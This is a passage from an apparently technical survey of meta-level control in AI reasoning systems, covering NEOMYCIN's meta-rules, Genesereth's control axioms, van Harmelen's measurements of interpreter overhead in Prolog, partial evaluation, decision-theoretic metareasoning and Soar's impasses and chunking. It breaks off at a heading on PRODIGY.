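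Suppose the program must determine whether a patient has had neurosurgery. It starts FINDOUT with neurosurgery as the subject. METARULE002 looks for a class that includes neurosurgery, finds surgery, and has the program first check whether the patient has had any surgery. If not, the program concludes that there was no neurosurgery without asking about it. The same meta-rule also works for cardiac surgery, because the second relation supplies the class.

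NEOMYCIN did not have this design at first. In the version that Clancey and Letsinger describe in *NEOMYCIN* (1981), each step from a specific finding to a more general one relied on its own screening rule. In their example consultation, the program needs to determine whether the patient has leukaemia. It first asks whether the patient is a compromised host, then whether the patient is immunosuppressed, and the user answers the second question with "leukemia". METARULE002 generalises all such screening rules.

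Other meta-rules can use the same relations for different purposes. If the user mentions neurosurgery, the program can conclude that the patient has had surgery. If the patient has had none of the kinds of surgery in the knowledge base, it can conclude that there was no surgery at all. That last inference would be wrong for a patient who had a kind of surgery missing from the knowledge base.

### Refining a diagnosis

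CENTAUR, a program Aikins developed in 1980, was a halfway stage between MYCIN, where the plan for refining a diagnosis was implicit, and NEOMYCIN, where it was explicit. CENTAUR explicitly recorded meningitis as a more specific kind of infection, so it could describe what it was doing better than MYCIN could. But it attached a separate instruction to each disease. The instruction for infection was to determine the specific disease once an infection was confirmed, and the instruction for meningitis was to determine the subtype once meningitis was confirmed. Both instructions apply the same strategy, but CENTAUR contained no general statement of it.

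In NEOMYCIN, METARULE001 states once how to refine a hypothesis: if the current hypothesis has a child that the program has not pursued, pursue that child. A child is a more specific disorder. For example, bacterial meningitis is a child of meningitis. If someone adds a new kind of infection to the hierarchy, the meta-rule applies to it immediately.

After Clancey took both kinds of strategy out of the medical rules, NEOMYCIN unexpectedly no longer needed to chain backward between those rules. MYCIN had therefore chained backward during diagnosis only to refine its hypotheses and screen its questions. Its engine had been supplying part of the diagnostic method, although MYCIN's builders regarded it as a neutral search procedure.

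### Evidence for the gains

The separation is of little use if it makes the diagnoses worse. Clancey (1985), in *Acquiring, Representing, and Evaluating a Competence Model of Diagnostic Strategy*, reports that NEOMYCIN's conclusions were "reasonably close" to MYCIN's on the ten meningitis cases that Yu and colleagues used for their blind evaluation. Earlier, Clancey and Letsinger had described preliminary runs with comparable results and fewer questions, but gave no figures. Clancey says that the 1985 evaluation discusses the issues and does not describe "formal, completed experiments".

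These comparisons are reassuring about accuracy, but they cannot isolate the effect of separating control, because NEOMYCIN also covered more diseases, such as migraine and brain abscess, and reasoned differently. It had to identify meningitis as a possibility from complaints such as a headache, whereas MYCIN's users told it that the patient had meningitis. Clancey and Letsinger attribute the shorter consultations to NEOMYCIN's more focused reasoning. A program with the same focus built into its medical rules might have asked just as few questions.

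Clancey's group demonstrated explanations of strategy in a working prototype. When NEOMYCIN asks about seizures, the user can see that it is testing the hypothesis of meningitis and which meta-rule selected that hypothesis. To keep its answers short, the explanation program skips tasks that merely apply rules and mentions those that shift attention, such as from a list of hypotheses to one of them. Clancey judged the level of description to be "apparently close" to the terms an expert would use, though some task names needed rewording. He was judging his own group's prototype, and his judgement doesn't show whether users could predict the program's next question or notice when its strategy was wrong.

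Whatever users think of the explanations, they are a reliable guide to the program's reasons because they come from the meta-rules that chose the question. This holds even if physicians reason differently. Clancey says the team inferred much of the procedure from Beckett's questions, rather than getting it directly from the expert, and filled it out with mathematical reasoning about how to search a set of possibilities.

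*Student modelling.* To teach diagnosis, a program has to work out what strategy a student is following. Clancey and colleagues treated NEOMYCIN's tasks as a grammar and tried to use it to parse a student's questions. Their program IMAGE worked from the general tasks down, and ODYSSEUS worked from the individual questions up. In Clancey's examples, ODYSSEUS interprets a question about seizures as a test for meningitis, but finds three consistent explanations for a question about fever. In 1986 the team was still testing ODYSSEUS on artificial students, made by altering NEOMYCIN's knowledge in known ways, so the method had been demonstrated but its accuracy was not yet known.

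In a classroom example, several students asked a patient one question after another about a sore throat, including whether gargling helped and whether the pain varied during the day. Clancey suggests that they may have been correctly trying to characterise the symptom without knowing which follow-up questions were useful, or that they may have had no hypothesis and been hoping for a clue. Both explanations involve the same written strategy and fit the same questions, but a teacher would respond to them differently.

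*Reuse.* Clancey generalised NEOMYCIN into HERACLES, a shell to which builders could add knowledge about another subject. EMYCIN had kept only MYCIN's engine, but HERACLES also kept NEOMYCIN's diagnostic procedure. With Tim Thompson, Clancey used it to build CASTER, which diagnoses faults in sand casting, a process for shaping metal. CASTER demonstrates that the procedure was not tied to medicine, but the lessons Clancey draws from it are about how to organise knowledge of causes and faults rather than how much work the shell saved. He says that generalising the design meant rethinking parts of NEOMYCIN, and describes HERACLES as an evolving idea rather than a finished tool.

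The one figure for how long reuse takes comes from the older tutoring program GUIDON, which kept its roughly 200 rules for conducting a lesson separate from its medical subject matter. The team connected it to SACON, a knowledge base about the structural analysis of objects, and got the combination working in about an hour, with a few changes for differences in notation. This is a single informal report about control over teaching, but it describes a real transfer between two very different subjects.

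*New facts without new control rules.* Clancey argues for this benefit from the design, and the examples above show why his argument is convincing. Adding a type of surgery means adding one relation, and METARULE002 will use it. But the benefit is limited to facts that fit an existing relation. Clancey points out that a new *strategy* often needs a new kind of relation. Considering common causes before serious but unusual ones, for instance, requires dividing the causes of every disorder into those two groups. By 1986 the meta-rules used about 170 relations. Davis's content reference makes new strategies easier to add, since a new meta-rule can often search for a feature that the ordinary rules already contain.

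The separation also helped with at least one correction. While working through an argument that the right hypothesis would always be considered, Clancey noticed that for one class of hypotheses the program never examined the more general categories above them, because the task that compares hypotheses lacked a meta-rule. Clancey recommends reasoning about the procedure in this way as a check alongside running cases.

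### What stayed implicit

NEOMYCIN comes much closer to complete control than TEIRESIAS, but some of its strategy still depends on order. The meta-rules within a task may be alternatives in order of preference or successive steps of a procedure. Clancey concedes that the program does not contain the reasons for the order. For example, it can pursue the siblings of a hypothesis before its children, but has no record of why it should. The clauses of MYCIN's rules had the same defect, but it is easier to manage in NEOMYCIN because a maintainer has 29 tasks to examine rather than hundreds of medical rules. By 1985 the team was adding notes on which orderings were arbitrary, which could reasonably vary between physicians, and which were essential to the model.

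Some control also remained among the medical facts. NEOMYCIN has relations that mark one finding as a good follow-up question to another, and trigger rules that make the program consider a disease as soon as certain findings appear. Clancey notes that the meaning of such relations depends on how the program uses them. A physician who marks a question as a useful follow-up to "headache" is therefore adding to the program's strategy, even though the entry is in the medical knowledge base. Clancey regards these associations as shortcuts experts have learned from experience, and thinks beginners need to learn some of them directly.

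A meta-rule cannot rewrite other meta-rules, so the control is protected from changes during a consultation. The facts it operates on are less secure, because NEOMYCIN treats its user as always reliable and cannot withdraw a conclusion after using it to reach others. If a user gives a wrong answer, a trigger rule may make the program investigate the wrong disease, and correcting the answer later will not undo the effects. Readable control rules do not solve this problem, because it can occur even when every meta-rule works as intended.

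Clancey also doubts that every skill has an abstract strategy to write down. Interpreting signals, for example, may depend on recognising patterns, with little deliberate choice about what to examine next. In other fields, people may have built up a procedure case by case that works well, though nobody can explain why. Even in medicine, some physicians are better than others at describing how they reason, and Clancey suggests working with good teachers because they are likely to have worked out the principles already. Beckett's help may therefore have made NEOMYCIN easier to build than a similar program in another field would be.

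Apart from the computation needed to run them, abstract meta-rules take more initial effort than rules for particular situations. Clancey accepts that this effort is unlikely to be worthwhile if nobody wants explanations, the original designers do all the maintenance, and they have no plans for a second system. But Clancey doubts even this exception, because designers who leave a knowledge base alone for a few months may no longer understand the strategies they built into it.

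## A separate interpreter for control and what it costs

Unlike TEIRESIAS, Genesereth's proposed architecture runs control as a separate process, and people can change its whole search strategy by editing one line of text. But it is slow, because every object-level step has to wait for meta-level reasoning. Van Harmelen measured the delay in Prolog and found it was much larger than researchers had generally estimated.

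### One pass through Genesereth's loop

The control program is a short LISP loop called SCHEDULER. On each pass it does four things:

1. It advances its clock by one.
2. It searches for a task that the control axioms recommend, meaning a value of *z* for which they imply RECOMMENDED(*z*).
3. It runs that task at the object level.
4. It records the task as EXECUTED.

The control axioms are logical statements about tasks. The loop uses them only in the second step, so an axiom affects the program's behaviour only if it helps to prove that some task is recommended. A person can find out why the program ran a task by reading the proof that the task was recommended. The record from the fourth step allows an axiom to exclude tasks that have already run.

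Suppose a diagnostic program wants to prove G. Its rules reduce G to the subgoals A and B, and it has started on A, which reduces to A1 and A2. It could now pursue B, at depth 1, or A1 or A2, at depth 2. A general axiom recommends any applicable task to which the program prefers no other applicable task. The search order then depends on one further axiom, and Genesereth gives two versions of it:

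```
depth-first:    DEPTH(IN(1,k1)) > DEPTH(IN(1,k2)) => PREFERRED(k1,k2)
breadth-first:  DEPTH(IN(1,k1)) > DEPTH(IN(1,k2)) => PREFERRED(k2,k1)
```

Here IN(1,k1) is the goal that task k1 would pursue. The first version gives priority to deeper goals, so the program goes on to A1 or A2 and leaves B until it has finished with A. This is depth-first search, the strategy built into Prolog. The second version gives priority to shallower goals, so the program works on B before A1 or A2 and finishes each level before starting the next. This is breadth-first search. The two axioms differ only in the order of k1 and k2 at the end, and the diagnostic rules don't have to change.

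Control axioms that are easy to read can still contain mistakes. If someone adds the second axiom and forgets to delete the first, the axioms rank A1 above B and B above A1, so they don't determine which to choose.

Neither version chooses between A1 and A2. Genesereth treats all recommended tasks as equally good, so the loop takes whichever its search finds first. A builder can therefore start with almost no control knowledge and add axioms one at a time, but control is complete only where someone has written enough axioms. Van Harmelen says that the published descriptions omit how the system makes the unspecified choices, and presumes that it uses some built-in strategy.

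Genesereth's group built several programs this way with MRS, a system for representing knowledge, including a tax adviser, a simulator for digital hardware and a new implementation of NEOMYCIN. For DART, which diagnosed faults in computer hardware, the group first wrote down facts about circuits and applied a general inference procedure to them. They then added control axioms to make it faster. Finally, they compiled many of the axioms into the inference procedure, partly by hand, which removed some of the separation they had started with. Genesereth reports that such programs were simpler to build and easier to modify, but gives no measurements.

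MRS also let users name the procedure that should handle a given kind of statement. Its manual called this complete modifiability, but the procedures were LISP code, so van Harmelen does not count it as the kind of modifiability explicit control requires.

### Which level does the work

Genesereth's loop is one of several ways to divide work between the levels. Van Harmelen classifies these designs by where activity takes place, from almost entirely at the object level to almost entirely at the meta level.

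*Object-level inference.* A version of Prolog by Gallaire and Lasserre has only an object-level interpreter, but users can write instructions that influence which condition it works on next and which rule it tries. One instruction might put shorter rules first. Another might make a condition wait until one of its variables has a value. With that instruction, a single definition of "grandparent" works efficiently whether someone is looking for Ann's grandchildren or her grandparents. Users cannot change the rest of the interpreter's loop, such as how it backs up after a dead end.

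In a reflect-and-act system, the levels alternate at every step. Hayes-Roth's BB1 is a blackboard system, in which specialised modules read from and write to a shared workspace. It has one blackboard for the problem and another for control. On each cycle, BB1 finds the modules that could run and chooses among them using heuristics from the control blackboard. Each heuristic has a weight, a written reason, an expiry condition and a function that rates possible actions from 0 to 100. If the user overrides a choice, BB1 starts a dialogue that can produce a new strategy for later cycles, so people can correct its control while it runs.

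In crisis management, the meta level runs only when the object level gets stuck. PDP-0, a model of how beginners solve thermodynamics problems, works this way. When a supervising component detects a dead end, it starts a second problem solver, which classifies the difficulty, picks a general repair and turns it into a specific change to the program's goals. This saves computation, but it gives an overseer little protection against an object level that is making steady progress in the wrong direction, because the meta level is never triggered.

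In *subtask management*, the meta level chooses a task, and the object level works on it until it succeeds or fails. Van Harmelen puts Genesereth's architecture in this class and calls its weakness the black-box effect, because the meta level cannot influence a task once it has started. This hides very little of the strategy if each task is a single inference, but could hide most of it if a task is a complete diagnosis. Van Harmelen also puts NEOMYCIN in this class, on the view that it has no explicit control while it solves a domain problem, although Clancey says that its meta-rules control every inference.

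PRESS, developed by Bundy, Welham and others, uses meta-level inference to solve algebra problems up to the level of English school-leaving exams. One of its meta-level rules applies to equations in which the unknown occurs exactly once, and solves them by finding the unknown and isolating it. Given log₂(*x* + 3) = 5, a program with this rule checks that *x* occurs once, uses a rule about logarithms to get *x* + 3 = 2⁵, and subtracts 3 to get *x* = 29. How many times *x* occurs and where are facts about the written equation, so the program is reasoning about object-level expressions throughout. The algebra rules are entries in the meta-level program, and PRESS has no separate object-level interpreter.

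PRESS benefits because searching among strategies is easier than searching among algebraic steps. There are fewer options at each point, and most wrong choices soon lead to a dead end. But some of its control is fixed. PRESS tries its strategies in a set order, applies the first that fits, and starts again at the top of the list. Another team rebuilt it with a third level that reasons about which strategy to select. Designers can keep adding levels, and 3-Lisp's tower of levels is infinite in theory, but in practice the top level always has built-in control.

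Van Harmelen prefers meta-level inference because it is the only class in which people can read and change the entire strategy. It comes closest to complete control on the four tests, but it also has the most overhead.

### One language or two

A designer must also decide whether the two levels share a language. Gallaire and Lasserre used Prolog for both. In a system with two languages, the meta level has a name for each object-level expression. For example, the object-level statement "drug(P, D)", with the variables P and D, might be named "drug(var(p), var(d))" at the meta level. This name contains no variables, so the control program can examine it without accidentally assigning values to P or D.

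With a shared language, D is also an ordinary variable of the control program, so a badly written control rule could set it to penicillin while merely choosing which medical rule to try. The answer would look as if the medical rules had produced it.

Van Harmelen adds that medicine and the control of inference are different subjects and may need different notations, and that the usual benefits of separation are harder to get if the two kinds of knowledge look alike. The two languages can still be of the same type, such as two copies of predicate logic, as long as they remain distinct.

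### Adding and suppressing conclusions

The object-level theory determines which conclusions are available, and the meta level determines which of them the program reaches. Van Harmelen calls a system *combinatorially sound* if it reaches only conclusions that follow from the object-level theory, and *combinatorially complete* if it reaches all of them.

An overseer may well want soundness without completeness. A meta level exists largely to abandon lines of reasoning that are unwanted or take too many resources, and this necessarily loses some conclusions. If the meta level can only suppress reasoning, a mistake in the strategy may cause the program to miss an answer, but it cannot make the program assert something that its domain knowledge does not support. The overseer can then let someone experiment with the strategy without rechecking the program's medical knowledge.

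This reassurance does not fully hold for programs that treat the absence of a proof as evidence. Suppose a program prescribes penicillin unless it can prove that the patient is allergic. If the meta level saves time by dropping the search for allergies, the program will prescribe penicillin to allergic patients. The meta level has suppressed one conclusion and thereby caused another that the full theory does not support.

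In van Harmelen's comparison, TEIRESIAS, BB1 and Genesereth's architecture are sound because their meta levels only choose among steps that the object level could take anyway. PRESS is not guaranteed to be sound, because its meta level specifies everything the object level does, including what counts as a solution, and that specification can be wrong. More complete control therefore tends to weaken the guarantee of soundness.

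Van Harmelen found the same problem in Socrates, the meta-level inference system described in the thesis. One of its control axioms specifies how to prove a compound statement from its two halves. If a user edits the axiom to require only the first half, Socrates will accept "the patient has an infection and is not allergic to penicillin" after checking only for infection. Socrates has no safeguard against this edit. NuPRL, a program for constructing mathematical proofs, prevents such mistakes by accepting a user's strategy only if it can establish that the strategy turns correct partial proofs into correct partial proofs.

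### The measured cost

To find out what the extra level costs, van Harmelen had three Prolog systems reverse a list of 30 items by a standard, deliberately naive method. Each system ran the task directly, then through an interpreter that shared its language, and then through an interpreter with a separate language. All of them used the same search strategy, so the results show the price of interpretation and none of the benefit of a better strategy. The figures are inferences per second on the list task:

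| Prolog system | Run directly | Shared language | Separate language |
|---|---|---|---|
| Edinburgh | 7,500 | 311 (24 times slower) | 0.7 (10,700 times slower) |
| Quintus | 20,000 | 850 (24 times slower) | 2 (10,000 times slower) |
| BIM | 17,000 | 326 (52 times slower) | 1.6 (10,600 times slower) |

The ratios are reliable to within about 20%. Reversing the list takes 496 inferences, so Quintus took about 0.025 seconds to do it directly, just over half a second with the shared language, and about four minutes with the separate one.

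The shared-language interpreter is three lines long because it leaves the handling of variables to the underlying Prolog system. The separate-language interpreter has to rename variables, match expressions and keep its own list of what each variable stands for. This list grows as the proof proceeds, so lookups take longer. The interpreter's slowdown therefore increased with input length, while the other two ran at a constant speed.

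A better strategy can make up for this, but only if it saves enough steps. If each step takes 24 times as long, the program runs faster only when it needs less than a twenty-fourth of the steps. Owen tried this with a theory of protein structure. The best result came from a special-purpose interpreter that reused intermediate results. It cut the number of inferences more than 300-fold but ran only twice as fast, so each remaining inference took more than 150 times as long as before.

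Lowe applied Owen's interpreters to simulations of electronic circuits. An interpreter that reordered goals as it ran beat plain Prolog on a circuit for adding binary numbers, but no other combination of interpreter and circuit did. On the adding circuit, the number of inferences grew in proportion to the circuit's size instead of exponentially. Such a saving eventually outweighs any fixed overhead per step. For instance, if one program needs 2ⁿ steps and another needs *n* steps that each take 100 times as long, they take about the same time at *n* = 10, and at *n* = 20 the second is about 500 times faster. Both studies used shared-language interpreters, which have less overhead than separate-language ones, so they do not show that the savings from a separate-language interpreter can outweigh its overhead.

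Van Harmelen notes that the 10,000-fold slowdown comes from the most extreme version of the separate-language interpreter, with every operation written out at the meta level. Operations such as matching expressions and renaming variables don't affect the strategy, so a designer could hard-wire them in fast code and leave only the strategic choices open to users. Van Harmelen estimated the effect for the simple task of joining two lists, counting each hard-wired operation as one inference. The interpreter then needed about 12 times as many inferences as plain Prolog, and the ratio no longer grew with the length of the list. Van Harmelen calls this estimate simplistic, since the hard-wired operations would still take more computation as proofs got longer.

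The thesis develops this idea into a design called partial reflection. The main loop is fixed, but users can program five of its steps: when to declare success, when to declare failure, which branch of the search to continue, which goal to work on there, and which new branches to discard. In a simulation, this design needed about a tenth as many inferences as the fully open interpreter, and its overhead grew much more slowly. A program can also check the design for soundness. The main requirements are that the step for discarding branches returns only branches it received, and that the system declares success only when some branch has succeeded. An overseer can no longer rewrite the main loop, but for most purposes that seems a good exchange for less computation and a stronger guarantee of soundness.

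### Merging the levels before running

Partial evaluation removes the overhead in a different way. A partial evaluator takes a program and the known part of its input, carries out every step that depends only on that part, and produces a new program containing the remaining steps. When the original program is a meta-level interpreter and the known input is a rule base, the new program merges the two levels. In van Harmelen's small example, two conclusions that had taken 18 and 41 inferences took one each afterwards.

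The merged program is faster, but its strategy is harder to read. Van Harmelen adapts an example from Clancey in which a general meta-rule puts rules whose conditions are likely to hold before rules whose conditions are not. Suppose the system also knows that Axiom 1 mentions a likely condition and Axiom 2 an unlikely one. The partial evaluator can then reduce the meta-rule and these two facts to a single instruction, "use Axiom 1 before Axiom 2". Someone who reads only this output sees the order but not the reason for it, as Clancey did with MYCIN.

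The general rule survives in the source text, where developers can still read and change it, but a change has no effect until they run the partial evaluator again. Control is therefore explicit only to people who have the source and the tools to rebuild the program. The source can also stop describing the agent's behaviour, for instance if someone patches the merged program directly.

Partial evaluation also works badly for some of the most useful kinds of control:

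- If the rule base changes during a run, the merged program is out of date. Builders can limit the damage by merging in only the stable rules and leaving out facts about the current case.
- A strategy may depend on the current problem or on progress so far, neither of which is known in advance. The partial evaluator must then stop early or generate code for every possibility, which can make the program enormous. Van Harmelen observes that all the published examples used strategies that depend on neither, and that such strategies are weak and general.
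- With recursive rules, the partial evaluator has to decide when to stop expanding them. No general test can always get this right, because it would solve the halting problem (deciding whether an arbitrary program will ever finish). A cautious test leaves the program slower than it could be, and a less cautious one may let the partial evaluator run for ever.

Genesereth suggests compiling only part of the control. In a graphics program, for example, the commands to draw, rotate or move a shape could be ordinary compiled code, except for one "hook" where each command calls the meta level to find the right procedure for that shape. Designers can keep hooks only where they expect to need flexibility. An overseer could use the same method to keep a few important decisions readable in an otherwise compiled agent.

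*Specifying Meta-Level Architectures for Rule-Based Systems* (Beetz, 1987) also separates the levels in the source but combines them in the running program. Users of Beetz's rule interpreter, CATWEAZLE, write control strategies separately from object-level rules. The system then compiles both into a single network of tests, using an extended version of RETE, an algorithm that stores partial matches to avoid repeating them. Beetz formally defines the meaning of one kind of strategy, a fixed sequence of phases, and proves that the procedure for running it is correct but incomplete, meaning that it stays within what the strategy allows but does not find everything the strategy allows. When the running form is no longer readable, such a proof gives people a reason to trust the written form as a description of the program.

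### When each step is a model call

The Prolog figures show such large slowdowns because the object-level steps were extremely fast. If an object-level step takes *s* seconds and control adds *m* seconds to it, the agent runs 1 + *m*/*s* times slower. In Quintus, a direct inference took 0.05 milliseconds and the separate-language interpreter raised this to half a second, which gives the factor of 10,000.

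Now suppose each object-level step is a two-second call to a language model, though real calls can be much shorter or longer. Even at the speed of a 1980s computer, the same half-second of control would make the agent take only 1.25 times as long. A realistic decision might need 20 such steps of control reasoning, or ten seconds on that computer. A machine 1,000 times faster would need ten milliseconds, or 0.5% of the time of the model call. The overhead that made separate interpreters impractical in Prolog is therefore negligible here, provided that the meta level is an ordinary program.

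If the meta level is a language model, the overhead is again substantial. A task of 20 two-second steps takes 40 seconds without control. Under the reflect-and-act arrangement, which adds an equally slow control call before every step, it takes 80 seconds, so the control calls would have to halve the number of steps to break even. Under crisis management, with control calls at only two steps, the task takes 44 seconds, but the meta level does not check the other 18 steps.

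Low-overhead control around a language model call is also less complete than control inside a Prolog interpreter. Van Harmelen's interpreter was slow, but it handled every inference, so a programmer could change any choice the program made. A program that surrounds a language model can decide whether to make a call and what to do with the result, but it cannot control the choices the model makes during the call. This is a large-scale case of the black-box effect. Designers can gain more control by dividing the work into smaller calls, but this increases the overhead. A half-second control decision before a two-second call adds a quarter to the running time. If designers replace that call with four half-second calls, they gain three more points at which to intervene, but a half-second decision before each call doubles the running time.

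## Deciding what to compute next

A control step before every model call can use more time than it saves, so an agent needs a way to tell which control steps are worth taking. One way is to use decision theory, which ranks actions by expected utility, the value of their possible outcomes weighted by likelihood. A computation also has consequences, because it takes time and may lead to a better action. Russell and Wefald (1989), in *On Optimal Game-Tree Search Using Rational Meta-Reasoning*, therefore treat each step of a program's search as a decision in the same sense as an action in the world. These decisions may not need a separate level, since an agent can also learn their results and then stop making them.

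### The value of a computation

Stuart Russell and Eric Wefald developed the general theory in *Principles of metareasoning* (1991). In simplified notation, the value of a computation is:

```
V(S) = U(a_S) - U(a) - TC(S)
```

S is a computation the agent could run next, such as simulating one more move in a game. The agent would take action *a* if it stopped thinking now, and action *a_S* after running S. U is the utility of an action, and TC(S) is the cost of the time that S takes. Since the agent cannot know the result of S in advance, it uses the expected value of the first two terms.

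A computation that cannot change the agent's action has no benefit. *Rational Metareasoning* (Liu, 1999), which summarizes a chapter in Russell and Wefald's book, lists this as one of two reasons not to compute. The other is that the time lost would outweigh the expected gain.

Suppose an agent must choose between two methods, where success is worth 1 and failure 0. Method A works half the time. Method B is untried, and its success rate is equally likely to be anything from 0 to 1, so its expected rate is also 1/2. The agent can simulate B once before choosing. If the simulation succeeds, the estimate for B rises to 2/3 and the agent picks B. If it fails, the estimate falls to 1/3 and the agent picks A, which is worth 1/2. The two results are equally likely, so the agent can expect 7/12 with the simulation and 1/2 without it, a gain of 1/12, or about 0.083. If running the simulation lowers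 the payoff by 0.05, the net gain is 0.033 and the agent should run it, but if it lowers the payoff by 0.10, the net loss is 0.017 and the agent should act at once.

A game-playing program can make the same calculation for each step of its search. Russell (2013), in *Fine-Grained Decision-Theoretic Search Control*, originally a conference paper from 1990, gives the expected benefit of examining a move other than the current favourite:

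```
expected benefit = ∫ p(x) (x - m) dx,   for x from m upwards
```

Here *m* is the favourite's rating, and *p(x)* is the probability density that the step will change the other move's rating to *x*. The integral starts at *m* because a lower rating would leave the favourite in place. Russell's program, MGSS2, takes the search step with the highest benefit minus cost, repeats this until no step's benefit exceeds its cost, and then plays the best move.

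Russell tested MGSS2 at the board game Othello against alpha-beta search, a standard method that looks a fixed number of moves ahead and skips branches that cannot affect the result. Both programs used the same function to evaluate positions. Against a two-move search, each side won eight games, and MGSS2 examined 9,280 positions while its opponent examined 44,866. Against a six-move search, MGSS2 won six games to two and examined about 76,000 positions while its opponent examined 4.6 million. These are few games, and the position counts leave out the time MGSS2 spent estimating which position to examine. But MGSS2 examined about 60 times fewer positions than the six-move search, so it could spend much longer on each one and still take less time overall.

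MGSS2 also controls more of its own computation than most of the systems so far, because its meta level chooses every position to examine and decides when to stop. Its numbers are easier to interpret than MOLGEN's priorities because each one estimates a gain in utility. But errors in U make those estimates less reliable. If the designers leave some harm out of U, the agent will see no value in a computation that would reveal the harm and will skip it to save time.

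### The regress

Estimating V(S) is itself a computation, so the agent could first work out whether the estimate is worth making, and before that, whether working this out is worthwhile. *Two Paradoxes of Bounded Rationality* (Thorstad, 2022) illustrates the regress with someone deciding how much to save for retirement. D0 is the basic choice among sums of money. D1 adds the option of deliberating first, with a choice of methods. D2 adds ways to choose the method, D3 adds ways to choose among those, and the series has no natural end.

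Some theorists look for a limit that the series approaches and define the rational choice at that limit. Thorstad doubts that such limits bear much on the problems people face, because each level takes far more work to solve than the one below and the benefits soon diminish. Russell and Subramanian observe in *Provably Bounded-Optimal Agents* that for programs too, choosing the best computations is often harder than solving the original problem, so doing it perfectly is seldom useful.

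MGSS and its successor stop the regress with a one-step estimate. They estimate the value of each computation as if it were the last one before acting. This takes so little computation that the program can do it without first calculating whether the estimate is worthwhile. Russell and Wefald show that the assumption that each computation is the last is "untenable in general", but their program still beat alpha-beta search.

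A fixed policy at the top also ends the regress. Horvitz and Breese (1990), in *Ideal Partition of Resources for Metareasoning*, consider an agent whose answer improves the longer it works, for example a medical program advising on treatment while a patient waits. Under their simplest model, the net utility of thinking for *t* seconds is:

```
u(t) = 1 - e^(-kt) - c(t + m)
```

The best thinking time is ln(*k*/*c*)/*k*, where *k* is the rate at which the answer improves and *c* is the utility lost per second of delay. The program needs a constant time *m* to calculate this. With *k* = 0.1, *m* = 0.01 and *c* = 0.04, the program should think for 9.16 seconds, for a net utility of 0.23. If *c* doubles to 0.08, it should think for only 2.23 seconds, and its net utility falls to 0.02. If *c* is 0.1, it should not think at all.

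When the designers wrote such a program, they decided that using the equation was worth a hundredth of a second, and no part of the program checks that decision. This makes the top level easy to control, because a person can read the formula, raise *c*, and predict that the program will answer sooner. But if the designers gave it the wrong *k*, the program will keep misjudging how long to think.

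### Thinking as a sequence of decisions

One-step estimates ignore the fact that computations can be useful together. Hay, Russell and colleagues (2014), in *Selecting Computations*, deal with this by treating the whole period of thinking as a Markov decision process, a standard model of step-by-step choices under uncertainty. In their metalevel decision process:

- The state is the list of results from all computations so far.
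- In each state, the agent either runs another computation, at a cost of *c*, or stops.
- When it stops, it takes the action with the highest expected utility, given those results.

The best policy maximises the expected utility of the final action minus *c* times the number of computations. *Learning to select computations* (2017) uses the agent's beliefs as the states and sets the value of stopping at zero. The agent then keeps computing as long as some computation has a positive value, counting the benefit of any further computations it leads to.

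The choice between methods A and B, which comes from one of Hay and colleagues' models, shows that the one-step estimate can make an agent stop too early. Suppose each simulation lowers the agent's payoff by 0.01, and the first has succeeded, so the estimate for B is 2/3. Another success would raise it to 3/4, and a failure would lower it to 1/2, level with A. Neither result would give the agent a reason to switch, so the one-step estimate of the gain is zero and the agent stops, however small the reduction per simulation. But if two more simulations both failed, the estimate for B would fall to 2/5 and A would be the better choice. This has a probability of 1/6 and would improve the outcome by 1/10, so the expected gain is 1/60, or about 0.017. The agent needs the second of these simulations only if the first fails, so the expected reduction is about 0.013, which is less than the gain, and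 the agent should continue.

Hay and colleagues prove that whenever the one-step policy would compute, the best policy would too, so an agent that uses one-step estimates may compute too little but never too much. They also prove an upper limit on the number of simulations the best policy runs in this model. The limit is 22 when each simulation carries a penalty of 0.01.

Other problems have no such limit, and a rational agent can lose more utility by deliberating than the decision is worth. In an example from Hay and colleagues, A again works half the time, and B's success rate is either 1/3 or 2/3, with equal probability. Whenever the agent has seen as many simulated successes as failures, its beliefs are back where they started, so it has the same reason to continue as it had at the beginning. If each simulation reduces utility by a small enough amount, the agent continues for as long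 as the results stay balanced. It eventually stops with probability 1, and the average number of computations is finite, but anyone who wants a guaranteed maximum must set one separately.

The best policy can also be hard to predict from its parts. In another of their examples, option 1 is worth −1.5 or 1.5 and option 2 is worth 0.25 or 1.75, each with equal probability, and finding out the value of either subtracts 0.2 from the agent's payoff. If the agent also has a sure option worth 0, it should check option 1 first. If the sure option is worth 1, it should check option 2 first, even though options 1 and 2 are the same as before. No fixed score for each computation can reproduce both choices, so a person who reads the scores one at a time, as in a list of rule priorities, will sometimes predict the wrong computation.

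Hay and colleagues tested an approximate version in Pachi, a program that plays Go by simulating games to the end. Their method chose which first moves to simulate and when to stop. On small boards, with a limit of 10,000 simulations per move, it won 64% of games against Pachi's existing method. The theory suits game programs unusually well because each simulation has a known cost and the result of a game clearly measures utility. A program that orders blood tests or edits someone's files rarely has reliable numbers for either.

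### Soar

John Laird, Allen Newell and Paul Rosenbloom developed Soar in the 1980s as a general architecture for intelligent behaviour. It chooses and applies operators, which are steps such as moving a block or turning left, and it bases the choice on preferences instead of utility estimates. Rules in its long-term memory propose operators and supply preferences about them, for instance that one operator is acceptable, better than another, or ruled out. All the rules that match can contribute at once, and a fixed decision procedure then uses the preferences to select an operator.

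If the preferences do not determine which operator to choose, for example because two operators tie or none is available, Soar reaches an impasse. It then creates a subgoal to resolve the impasse and pursues that subgoal with the same rules and decision procedure as any other goal. Suppose a delivery robot reaches a junction and its rules produce no preference between turning left and turning right. In the subgoal, it can simulate each turn, find that the left corridor ends at a locked door, and produce a preference for turning right, which resolves the impasse.

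*Agentic Cognitive Depth* (Upreti, Sypherd and Belle, 2026) cites these subgoals as an example of meta-level control in a cognitive architecture. The subgoals resemble what van Harmelen calls crisis management, because Soar reasons about its own choices only when it cannot make one. This also limits the regress. An impasse within a subgoal leads to a further subgoal, but Soar stops deliberating about a choice once the available knowledge settles it.

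Chunking saves Soar from repeating the deliberation. When a subgoal produces a result, Soar traces which facts from outside the subgoal the result depended on, and builds a new rule that goes directly from those facts to the result. The robot might acquire the rule "if the destination is the office and the left door is locked, prefer right at this junction". This rule, called a chunk, joins the others in long-term memory. At the same junction the next day, the chunk fires at once, and the robot turns right without reaching an impasse or opening a subgoal.

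A person who wants to follow the robot's reasons can learn much more from the first day, because the subgoal contains the alternatives and the imagined locked door, whereas the chunk contains only the conditions and the preference. The same loss occurs when a partial evaluator merges a strategy into a rule base, but in Soar it happens while the agent is working, and no developer starts it. Chunking also makes mistakes harder to correct, because fixing the rules that the robot used to imagine the corridors does not remove the chunks it has already built from them.

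### PRODIGY and the utility problem

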